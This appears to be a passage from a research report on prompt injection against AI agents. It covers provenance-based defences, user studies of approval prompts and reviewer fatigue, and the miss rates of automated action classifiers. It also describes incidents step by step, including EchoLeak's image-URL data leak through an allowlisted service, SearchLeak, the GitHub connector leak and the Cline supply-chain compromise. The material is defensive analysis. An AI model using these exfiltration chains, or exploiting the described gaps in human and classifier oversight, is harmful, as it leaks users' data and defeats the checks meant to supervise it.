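Users often request actions whose details appear only in a document. In one of ROPE's test tasks, a user asked an agent to fetch an electricity bill from a website and pay it, but the account number appeared only in the bill. Although there was no attack, ROPE refused the payment because it could not distinguish the real account number from one a criminal might have put in its place.

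Of 411 runs without an attack, 96 failed after ROPE had refused a call. In 83 of them, the value the agent needed appeared only in text that an attacker could have written. In another 10, the agent had reworded a phrase, such as the title of an event, so it no longer matched the request. Shavit's audit fails when the plan leaves out a tool that the task needs, which happened in at least 15% of his clean tasks.

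Better records can fix some of these cases. The accounts assistant can pay Northfield under ROPE's rules because the account number is in the company's supplier register, which counts as a protected record if the assistant can't write outside text into it. If Northfield changes banks, the software will refuse to pay the new account until an employee has updated the register, which is a reasonable delay for a payment. The electricity company's customer could likewise save the account number once and pay every later bill automatically.

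Other tasks don't specify which actions the agent should take. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an agent that is asked to summarise a problem report, finds that it depends on a second report and decides to summarise both. The first report changed what the agent did, as an injection would, but the user would be pleased with the result. They suggest judging such a change by its source and extent.

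*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) presents a system called SARA. As in AgentTracer, outside text may fill in a detail of the user's task, such as the name of a file to send, but can't add a new task. SARA keeps a lasting record of any action that outside text has suggested. Before making a call with real effects, it looks for support in the user's request and in the results of earlier authorised calls. Attacks succeeded at most 0.63% of the time in the paper's four main tests. Because SARA relies on models to interpret the text, it lacks the firm guarantee that ROPE gets from comparing values.

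Users sometimes leave the whole decision to someone else, as in "do what John's email asks". Software can confirm that the email came from John, but it has no other statement of the user's wishes to compare with the agent's actions. It can block everything the request doesn't mention, which makes the agent useless for this job, or allow whatever the email asks. Progent instead asks the user whenever the task seems to need wider permissions. In its AgentDojo tests, only 6% of changes to the permission rules needed approval.

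## Does asking a person to approve an action help?

An approval prompt lets a person allow or refuse an action before it runs. It is useful when software can't determine whether the user wanted the action, and it suits cases that fixed rules handle badly, such as when a supplier really has changed banks. But it works only if the person gets the facts needed to decide and still reads them after hundreds of harmless requests.

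### What the prompt has to show

Suppose the accounts assistant's payment system asked Patel about unknown bank accounts instead of refusing them. For the doctored invoice, a useless prompt might look like this:

```
The assistant wants to pay Northfield's invoice 2291.
[Allow]   [Always allow]   [Refuse]
```

A useful prompt for the same payment would contain much more:

```
PAY            GBP 1,840.00
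to account     00-00-00 55667731
   source      text of invoice 2291, from an outside sender
   warning     not in supplier register; Northfield's
               account there is 00-00-00 10428816
amount from    invoice 2291; matches purchase order 7730
data sent      payment reference "2291" only
your request   "Deal with the new invoices"
undo           you can cancel until 09:14 tomorrow, not later
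[Refuse]   [Allow once]
```

Patel has no reason to refuse the first request. In the second, she can see that the account number came from outside the company and differs from the one on file. She can then phone Northfield on a number the company already had.

The software that executes the call should write the approval prompt, because the prompt's text can be manipulated. The software should also run exactly the call that the person approved. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) recommends a new check if any argument changes after the review.

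Showing a person the exact arguments isn't always enough, particularly for commands. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of problems with agents and files. In 31 of them, the approval prompt showed a command but not its effect on the user's files. For example, a person who approves "python3 setup.py" allows whatever that script contains.

Other requests look harmless because the problem occurred in an earlier step. In an example from Hossain and colleagues, a user tells an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. An injected instruction leads the agent to copy raw invoice rows into report.csv, and the agent then asks for approval to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are fine, so the reviewer needs to know what went into the file.

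The researchers tested four prompts on 80 volunteers, 20 for each design. Every volunteer judged 12 requests, half of them malicious.

| What the prompt showed | Malicious requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Also the user's original limits and a log in time order | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
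| The same facts, organised around the action's consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. The further gain from organising those facts could be chance, since the 95% interval for the difference runs from 19.7 points fewer unsafe approvals to 3.8 points more. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the malicious requests. Half the requests in the test were attacks, whereas reviewers at work see attacks far less often and so have less reason to stay alert.

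### How often people catch a bad action

The largest test comes from Anthropic, which wanted to replace approval prompts. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study of 1,053 paid testers who used the company's coding agent. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one approval prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

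The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a developer would, which may have lowered the overall rate. But that doesn't obviously explain why the rate fell during a session, as it would if the testers were getting tired.

People did better in a shorter test with plain descriptions. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) studied 113 people from outside the software industry. They supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task. Participants who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of those seven. However, these actions weren't attacks, and some users may have wanted them. Of this group, 88% approved a call to the airport to confirm a flight, while 21% approved a public post about the user's travels.

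People notice even less when nothing prompts them at the critical moment. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) manipulated agents, for instance through a hidden note in a job applicant's CV, and had 303 people work with them. With only a general warning at the start, participants noticed something wrong in 8.6% of cases. When an alert interrupted them at the suspicious output, the rate rose to 25%. Technical experts did no better than other users.

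A reviewer's confidence is also a poor guide to whether they have caught a problem. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) watched 36 people do programming tasks with a coding agent. They readily spotted faults that caused a visible failure, but were often highly confident while missing faults that didn't. A successful injection usually causes no visible failure, because it sends the stolen file in an ordinary email.

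Supervision still has some value. *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025) reports that in 14 of 16 tasks, people were less likely to fall for manipulative web designs when they supervised an agent. But they focused on the path the agent had chosen and noticed less of the rest of the page.

### What a high acceptance rate shows

Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. By August 2026, Anthropic put the figure at 97%. Most requests are legitimate and should be approved, so these rates don't prove that users click without reading. OpenAI's automatic reviewer for Codex can't get tired, yet it approves about 99% of the requests it receives, according to Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*.

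If one approval prompt in 10,000 is malicious, a perfect reviewer accepts 99.99% of prompts and someone who approves everything without reading accepts 100%. The acceptance rate is therefore almost useless for estimating how many attacks a reviewer would catch.

Anthropic also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual requests. This suggests that people think harder about plans, although a plan also contains more to disagree with. Users' settings are stronger evidence that they don't want to read prompts. In the same data, 62% of users had either used a mode that skips permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.

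A long run of approvals isn't a reason to stop asking for approval. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or the need to get on with the work, rather than growing trust.

A company has to test reviewers to find out whether they pay attention. Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi (2026), in *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop*, suggest planting known errors and counting how many the reviewer catches. A reviewer who misses the errors may need a break or more training. Mitchell and colleagues acknowledge that this is a form of workplace surveillance and that managers could misuse the results.

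### How many prompts it takes to stop one attack

Let p be the share of prompts that are malicious and d the share of those that the reviewer catches. On average, the number of prompts read for each attack caught is

1 / (p × d).

If one prompt in 10,000 is malicious and the reviewer catches half of those, the reviewer must read 1 / (0.0001 × 0.5) = 20,000 prompts for each attack caught. At 33 seconds each, roughly the time people took with the best prompt in the study by Hossain and colleagues, that takes about 180 hours. If Patel saw 20 prompts each working day, she would catch one attack and approve another about every 1,000 working days, or four years.

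If her detection rate fell to 5%, she would answer 200,000 prompts for each attack she caught. Mistaken refusals are a further drawback. If she wrongly refused 1% of legitimate requests, she would block about 200 of them for each attack she stopped. That might be worthwhile to protect the whole customer file, but not to prevent a loss of £1,840.

### Asking less often

A reviewer reads far fewer approval prompts per attack caught if the software asks only about high-risk actions. Suppose these are one action in 50 and include every attack. The share of prompts that are malicious then rises from one in 10,000 to one in 200, and a reviewer who catches half the attacks reads 400 prompts for each one caught. This depends on the software classifying actions correctly, since nobody will review an attack that it treats as low-risk.

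Isolating the agent removes many approval prompts because the agent can work freely inside fixed boundaries. In October 2025, Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reported that isolation had cut prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. That figure doesn't show whether people read the remaining prompts more carefully.

Developers can also use a model to decide which actions need approval. *Magentic-UI* (2025), a research system for supervised agents, instructs a model to require approval for anything irreversible or potentially harmful, and to ask when unsure. For example, the agent needs approval to type sensitive information into a website, but not to run an ordinary web search.

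In Yan's study, people who set standing rules blocked about 20 percentage points less of the unwanted behaviour than people who reviewed each action. The rules were "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money. People chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, then approved two thirds of the unwanted actions they were asked about. Those who reviewed each action approved only 40% of unwanted actions.

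**Approving a whole plan** replaces many small decisions with one that people seem to take more seriously. But the user approves the plan before the agent has read any untrusted content, so the approval protects them only if software makes the agent follow the plan, as CaMeL does. The plan also can't include an account number that the agent hasn't seen yet. For invoices, it would be better to let the assistant read them all and prepare the payments, then show Patel one list with any unfamiliar accounts at the top. Mitchell and colleagues recommend this kind of batch review because people can judge related actions together.

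**A second person** can check large transfers. Mitchell and colleagues suggest this for consequential actions and recommend reviewers who don't benefit from the approval. If two reviewers each caught half of all attacks independently, together they would catch 75%. If each caught 13.6%, the rate in Anthropic's test, together they would catch about 25%. Real reviewers would probably do worse than this, because they see the same prompt and may each rely on the other. The second person should therefore check something different, for instance by phoning the supplier. That takes several minutes, so it suits a few large payments better than every invoice.

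### Classifiers that replace prompts

Anthropic and OpenAI now use models to make many of the decisions they once left to users. In Claude Code's auto mode, the agent can read files and edit them within the project without review. A classifier checks other actions, such as running commands. According to Anthropic, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Like Shavit's guardian, it doesn't receive the text that tools return. It also doesn't receive the agent's explanations, so they can't lead it to a bad decision.

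The classifier works in two stages. A quick first check flags 8.5% of harmless calls. A slower second check reasons about the flagged calls and reduces that rate to 0.4%. When the classifier blocks a call, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code prompts a person for approval.

OpenAI's Auto-review checks only actions that would take Codex outside its sandbox. In a snapshot of 10,000 actions that Trębacz and colleagues use as an illustration, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which rejected seven. Codex found another way in four of those cases and stopped to ask the user in the other three. With Auto-review, sessions stop for human approval about 200 times less often than in manual mode.

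An independent test of such classifiers gave much worse results than the companies' own tests. In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) used many vague requests, such as an order to delete old files with no mention of whose files the agent could delete. They then repeated the checks on the same actions with the permitted scope stated in the request.

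| Classifier and test | Bad actions missed | Legitimate actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic: 52 real actions that went beyond the user's wishes | 17% | 0.4% |
| Anthropic: 1,000 synthetic data thefts | 5.7% | 0.4% |
| Anthropic: the dangerous commands from the tester study | 11% | Not reported |
| Trębacz and colleagues: synthetic actions that went beyond the user's wishes | 9.7% | About 1% |
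| Trębacz and colleagues: synthetic prompt injections | 0.7% | About 1% |
| Yang and colleagues: vague requests to Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code | 54%, 93% and 80% | 37%, 10% and 31% |
| Yang and colleagues: the same actions with the scope stated | 8%, 20–26% and 20% | 2%, 3% and 2% |

Anthropic's 17% miss rate represents only about nine missed actions. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classed the action as one the user had consented to. OpenAI's 0.7% covers only attacks that run external code, steal secrets or upload data. When Trębacz and colleagues included deletion and tampering, the miss rate rose to 9.8%, though they considered many of the extra misses minor.

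In the tester study, the classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, and people caught only six of those it allowed. Using both would have blocked 89.6%.

Anthropic also commissioned a prompt injection test from Trajectory Labs. None of 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded without it, so the test is weak evidence of how much protection auto mode adds. Auto-review cut the success rate against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03% to 5.83%, a more informative result. The attacks had been optimised against an older Claude model, so the results are a poor basis for comparing the two companies.

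A system could ask a person to review only the calls its classifier blocks. If one of 10,000 calls were an attack, the person would have about 41 calls to review, probably including the attack, at the rates Anthropic measured for harmless calls and data theft. But letting the person overrule the classifier would weaken the protection. If they recognised only half of the blocked attacks, the share of attacks stopped would fall from 94% to 47%. For data theft, Claude Code therefore offers no approval button in auto mode. The user has to leave that mode or run the command personally.

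Classifiers don't offer the certainty of a fixed limit. Trębacz and colleagues found cases where Auto-review could be misled into approving commands, and they don't expect such systems to give firm guarantees.

### What companies require now

Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, tested five commercial agents in May and June 2026. ChatGPT's chat mode required approval for every action that its permission settings covered. They found no way to grant approval in advance, although OpenAI's documentation describes such an option for some low-risk actions. In ChatGPT's agent mode, which operates a remote browser, they couldn't set any permissions for the browser, though the user has to watch the agent on certain sites.

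OpenAI's dots still need the user's approval for each purchase, while Anthropic has since moved away from individual prompts.

| Product | When a person decides |
|---|---|
| Codex | When an action would leave the sandbox, unless Auto-review is on |
| Claude Code, by default since August 2026 on most paid individual and team plans | When Claude asks, or after repeated blocks |
| Most Claude apps, by default since late October 2026 on the Pro, Max and Team plans | An automatic check replaces approval of each action |

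*Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) reports that later versions of Claude Code start in auto mode on every plan. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems. A company that gives an agent access to its bank account shouldn't assume the default settings require a person to approve each payment.

### Who is responsible for a bad approval?

Mitchell and colleagues argue that users now bear almost all the burden of overseeing agents. Companies tell people to check an agent's work but rarely give them the means to do it well. The agent produces more text than anyone can follow, and relying on it erodes the skills needed to check its work. If Patel approved the useless prompt, the record would show that she authorised a fraudulent payment, even though the software never displayed the account number to her.

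Mitchell and colleagues argue that better explanations and logs are necessary, but that an organisation also has to give reviewers time and breaks, and mustn't reward them for approving as much as possible. *When Agents Act Unwatched* (2026) adds that a human check isn't a meaningful control if the person sees the wrong evidence, or sees the right evidence too late.

Some decisions belong to the user because only the user knows the answer. In the tests by Yang and colleagues, 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions broke a limit that appeared neither in the request nor in anything the agent had read. Neither stronger models nor more background information consistently helped the classifiers. When the requests stated the limits, the agents proposed no out-of-scope actions in 384 new runs.

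This justifies asking users what they want, preferably before the agent starts, but not expecting them to find an attack in a stream of technical requests. Patel can reasonably be held responsible for deciding whether the assistant may pay a new supplier, but the company and its software provider should be responsible for making sure she can see where the account number came from.

They also have to enforce her refusal. One user interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* refused several requests, but the agent then continued by another route, and the user couldn't tell whether it was still respecting the limit. If Patel refuses the payment to the unknown account, the payment system should block that account for the rest of the run, whichever tool the assistant tries next.

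## What damage still gets through?

Several widely used AI products have leaked data or carried out an attacker's commands even though they had some of the limits described above. Researchers demonstrated EchoLeak, SearchLeak and a leak through GitHub, none of which has known victims. An attack on the coding tool Cline put unwanted software on other people's computers. Ordinary businesses have also tried to plant recommendations in the memory of people's AI assistants, but it is not known whether they succeeded.

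### Data leaves through a permitted channel

In January 2025, the company Aim Security found that one email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot leak confidential data. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, reconstruct the attack:

1. The attacker emails an employee. The instructions read like an ordinary business request, so Microsoft's injection detector misses them.
2. The employee later asks Copilot a question about work. Copilot retrieves the email along with internal files and follows its instructions.
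3. Copilot's answer includes an image whose address contains confidential details. A filter normally removed outside links from answers, but it missed a less common way of writing them.
4. The employee's browser automatically requests the image. It may load images only from approved domains, but one of these hosts a Microsoft Teams service that fetches other addresses on request. Teams passes the data to the attacker's server.

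The allowlist worked as designed, since the browser contacted only Microsoft. Copilot didn't send an email or change a file, so limits on those actions wouldn't have helped.

Copilot's audit record should have listed the email among the items Copilot used, but shown no detected injection. The leak would have appeared only in the text of the answer and in network records. The employee had little reason to report anything, because the email contained instructions for Copilot not to mention it and the image just looked broken.

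Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025 and said it had no evidence that attackers had used it. According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips embedded images and the less common links from outside content. In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, Willison (2025) counted a dozen products that had already had similar leaks.

A year later, data could leave Copilot through another approved Microsoft service. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot's search of company emails, meetings and files. Copilot treated the search query in a web link as instructions, so when an employee clicked the attacker's link, Copilot searched the mailbox and put an email's subject line, which might include a login code, into an image address. Microsoft's safeguard turned such images into plain text only after Copilot had finished writing, and by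 then the browser had already requested the image. The request went to Bing, an approved domain, and Bing's image search fetched the attacker's address.

Here the instruction came from a link rather than from content Copilot retrieved, so a log could record the attacker's words as the employee's request. Software that compared Copilot's actions with that request would have approved the search. Microsoft has fixed this flaw too, and ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* reported no known attacks that used it. It advises administrators to look for Copilot links with unusual queries and for abnormal connections to Bing's image service. Varonis also recommends checking allowlists for any site that fetches addresses supplied by users, since such a site can forward data anywhere.

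### Permitted actions combine into a harmful one

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates a leak in which every step was an ordinary use of the account. The researchers connected Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to a GitHub account with a public game project and several private projects. Anyone on GitHub can post an issue, such as a bug report, on a public project, and the researchers posted one containing instructions. When the user asked Claude to look at the open issues, it read the private projects and copied details from them, including the user's salary and plan to move to South America, into a proposed change to the public game.

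By default, Claude Desktop asked the user to approve each call, but Invariant Labs reports that many users choose "Always Allow". A log that records each call's full arguments would show the whole sequence, as the researchers' trace does.

Invariant Labs, which sells software for enforcing such rules, suggests limiting an agent to one project per session. That would have stopped this leak, because the session started in a public project that contained nothing private. It would also block legitimate work across two projects, and it wouldn't help if outsiders could post in the project that held the private data.

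Invariant Labs argues that GitHub couldn't solve the problem alone, because its connector had no coding error to fix. In August 2025, GitHub added a scan for passwords and other credentials in tool calls that involve public projects (GitHub, 2025). The scan reduces one serious kind of leak, but it doesn't detect other private information, such as salaries or travel plans.

The attack on Cline depended on the combination of two separate automated jobs. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) explains that in December 2025 the company set up a job in which Claude read each new GitHub issue and could run commands to investigate it. The job had only read access to Cline's source code, and this limit held. But the job shared a cache, a store of reusable files, with another job that published new versions every night. Someone who got Claude to run a command could plant files in the cache, and the publishing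 job would load them and expose its credentials.

Adnan Khan, a security researcher, reported the flaw privately on 1 January 2026. Cline didn't act until he published it on 9 February. The company then removed the job within 30 minutes and began replacing its credentials. Staff deleted the wrong access token for npm, a service that distributes software packages. They checked npm's management page, which showed no active tokens, but the exposed one still worked. On 17 February, somebody used the exposed token to publish a version of Cline that also installed OpenClaw, another AI agent.

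The altered version was available for about eight hours, and LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) reports about 4,000 downloads. The damage was small because OpenClaw is legitimate software. An attacker with the same access could have delivered a program that stole passwords.

Cline used its records to compare every release since December with the source code and the publishing jobs, and found no other unauthorised version. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, found the probable start of the attack outside those records, in a deleted issue that he recovered from a public archive of GitHub activity. Someone had posted the issue on 28 January, closed it about five minutes later and changed its title to "user error". Bargury couldn't recover the program that the poster told Claude to install, so the archive doesn't show every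 step of the theft. He concludes that the attacker was probably a bug hunter who had copied Khan's publicly visible tests. According to the AI Incident Database, Khan says that he tested only on a copy of Cline's project.

Cline has since removed the AI job and says any replacement will be read-only and unable to run commands. Publishing jobs no longer use the cache, and Cline no longer keeps long-lived npm tokens. Staff must test that an old credential has stopped working and not rely on a management page to confirm it.

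### Saved memory carries the instruction into later sessions

Limits that apply to one session, such as Invariant Labs' rule, don't cover what an assistant remembers afterwards. Microsoft's *That helpful “Summarize with AI” button*, published in February 2026, describes website buttons that open the visitor's AI assistant with a ready-made prompt to summarize the page and remember the company behind the site as a trusted source. If the assistant saves this to memory, it may treat it as the user's own preference when giving advice weeks later.

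In 60 days of email traffic, Microsoft found 50 different prompts of this kind from 31 real businesses, including some in health and finance and one security vendor. Microsoft counted attempts, not successful changes to memory, and says the results varied between assistants and over time. An attempt could work only if the assistant accepted a new memory from a prompt the user hadn't written.

Microsoft provides log searches that find these links in emails and Teams messages and identify users who clicked them. The searches cover at most 30 days of raw data, but a saved note can last much longer. A company that investigates a strange recommendation in June may find the note but not the click that created it in February. Copilot users can view and delete saved memories, and Microsoft says it has added filters and other protections. Microsoft could no longer reproduce some of the previously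 reported behaviour.

An injected document can plant a memory in an AI system without the user clicking anything. Chu cites an attack that inserted false memories with a 98.2% success rate using only ordinary queries. But in his survey of research up to April 2026, he found no benchmark that tests attacks that build up over several sessions. Low failure rates on current benchmarks are therefore weak evidence that systems are safe from planted memories.

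| Case | What the AI read | What it did | Limits | What logs could show | Vendor's change |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, 2025, demonstration | An outside email and internal files | Put private data in an image address | Allowlist included a service that forwards requests | The email, but no detected attack | Strips images and some links from outside content |
| GitHub connector, 2025, demonstration | A public issue and private projects | Published private details | No rule against combining public and private projects | The full sequence of permitted calls | Scans for credentials |
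| Cline, 2026, attack with victims | Probably a public issue | Probably ran a command that exposed credentials | Read-only access to code held; jobs shared a cache | Unauthorised release; issue survived in a public archive | Removed the AI job, the shared cache and long-lived tokens |
| SearchLeak, 2026, demonstration | A clicked link and the user's mailbox | Put an email's subject in an image address | Allowlist included Bing, which forwarded the request | An unusual link and a connection to Bing | Fixed on Microsoft's servers |
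| Recommendation prompts, 2026, real attempts | A prompt in a clicked link | Saved a biased note, if the attempt worked | Some assistants may have accepted the note | The link, for up to 30 days | Filters and memory controls |

### A distorted answer needs no tool call

An attacker may want only to change what the AI tells its user. Suppose Patel asks the accounts assistant to compare quotes from three suppliers, and a hidden line in one quote makes the assistant leave out that supplier's delivery charge. Patel then signs that supplier's contract herself, not knowing that delivery makes it more expensive. The assistant has only read three documents and written an answer, so there is no action to block or approve. The log looks normal, and somebody would have to compare the answer with the quotes to find the omission.

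The risk from a browser AI that can only summarise depends partly on what people do with the summary. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* quotes Mayur Sewani of the security company Forcepoint, who calls such an AI "low-risk", which is reasonable if the main concern is stolen data or money. But Unit 42 (2026), the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, found a scam page with hidden instructions meant to get AI systems that review advertisements to approve it, an attack that would need only a false verdict to succeed.

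This kind of manipulation is already common enough to measure. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) found about 1,500 injections on the web that tried to improve or damage a reputation. The paper also reports 5,200 tests in which 13 models summarised pages containing injected instructions. Smaller models followed the instructions up to 8% of the time when they received the page as plain text. The rate was between 0.2% and 1.1% when the input preserved the page's structure, which helps a model identify, for example, a line that came from a hidden comment. Even a low rate matters here because the only remaining safeguard is the reader, who has no reason to be suspicious.

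### What logs can help to reverse

Logs can help undo damage when the company still controls whatever the agent changed. An administrator can restore an overwritten file, delete a false memory or cancel a payment that the bank is still holding, if the log identifies it. The damage was harder to undo in the Cline case. Cline replaced the altered package the same day, but people who had already installed it had to remove OpenClaw from their own computers.

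A company can't recover a stolen credential, but it can cancel it. Records can help show which credentials an attacker could have reached, but staff still have to cancel the right ones, which Cline at first failed to do.

Other data can't be made private again once it has been disclosed. Deleting the GitHub page with the user's salary, for example, wouldn't remove copies that other people had made. Logs can only document such a leak. The company can use the accounts assistant's log to work out which version of the customer file leaked, and so which customers to warn about fraudulent bills. Without the log, it might have to assume that the attacker had everything the assistant could read.

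A company can sometimes undo the effects of bad advice. If it logs which saved notes entered the model's input on each run, it can find every recommendation that a false note might have affected. It can then review the decisions based on those recommendations, though a signed contract may still be binding.

### What is known of criminal use in 2026

Criminals are experimenting with indirect prompt injection, but there is little public evidence that they have made much money from it. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground* (July 2026) reports that underground forums advertise tools that hide instructions in emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages, with subscriptions starting at about $150 a month. Proofpoint calls these methods experimental and hasn't seen criminals use them regularly or at scale. It suspects criminals have little reason to change their methods while deceiving people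 directly still works so well.

Some malicious pages are already live. Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes two campaigns, a payment scam and a site that impersonated a cryptocurrency platform. In the payment scam, the attacker asked agents for 0.0012 ether, a few dollars at most. According to SC Media, the attacker's wallet had received payments, but none of that amount, so its payment history doesn't show that any agent paid. Zscaler's Amit Banker suspects that the attacker kept the sum low to stay within agents' spending limits.

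OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), an entry with an AI-generated summary in a public incident monitor, states that the two campaigns caused financial losses. The wallet's records don't establish this, so counting such entries may overstate the harm.

Broad searches of the web have found many injections but few sophisticated attacks. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* describes a search of static websites that Google reported in April 2026, using an archive that collects 2–3 billion pages a month. Many of the matches were articles about prompt injection. A small number of real injections tried to steal data, such as a computer's password file. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes Google's conclusion that attackers didn't yet seem to be using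 published research at scale. Forcepoint's ten examples from the same month included attempts to commit fraud, destroy data and steal access keys.

Many injections come from website owners who want to keep AI systems away. Khodayari and colleagues found confirmed injections on 9,676 of 1.2 billion pages, or about one in 124,000, and the sites' own operators had written about 81% of them. The most common type told the AI to return random numbers. Companies may also use injections to seek data from users' machines. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud said in December 2026 that it would stop sending AI agents prompts that sought local data, which had been part of its measures against abuse.

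### Why low incident counts don't show that agents are safe

An attack enters the public count only if the victim notices the harm, traces it to an injection and reports it. Let N be the number of successful attacks, and let d, a and r be the shares that pass each of these stages, among the attacks that passed the stage before. The expected number of reports is

N × d × a × r.

If each share were 30%, 100 successful attacks would produce about three reports. Nobody knows the real shares, so few reports could mean that attacks are rare or that most go unreported.

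At the first stage, victims can easily miss an attack. EchoLeak would have left a broken image, and a distorted summary might leave no visible sign. At the second stage, a company that pays a doctored invoice may record it as ordinary invoice fraud, especially if it hasn't kept the text its agent read. At the third, the company may have no duty to publish what happened, or may leave out part of it. Cline's public account doesn't mention the January issue that Bargury found. He could find it because GitHub issues are public and an independent archive had kept a copy, whereas a malicious email to a private company would leave no such public record.

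Web searches can also miss some injections. Khodayari and colleagues searched for 3,963 known phrases, such as orders to ignore previous instructions, and checked the matches by hand. This method could miss an injection worded as a normal business request, like the one in EchoLeak. It also partly explains why 99% of the injections they found openly tried to override the AI's task. Google's study left out social media, and neither study could search private email, where an attacker would send a doctored invoice.

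Microsoft's statement that it had no evidence of attacks using EchoLeak is somewhat stronger evidence than a lack of public reports, because the company runs the service and can examine its records. But Reddy and Gujral don't say which records Microsoft checked or how far back it looked. The flaw existed for at least four months, and the attack's last step looked like a browser loading an image from Microsoft.
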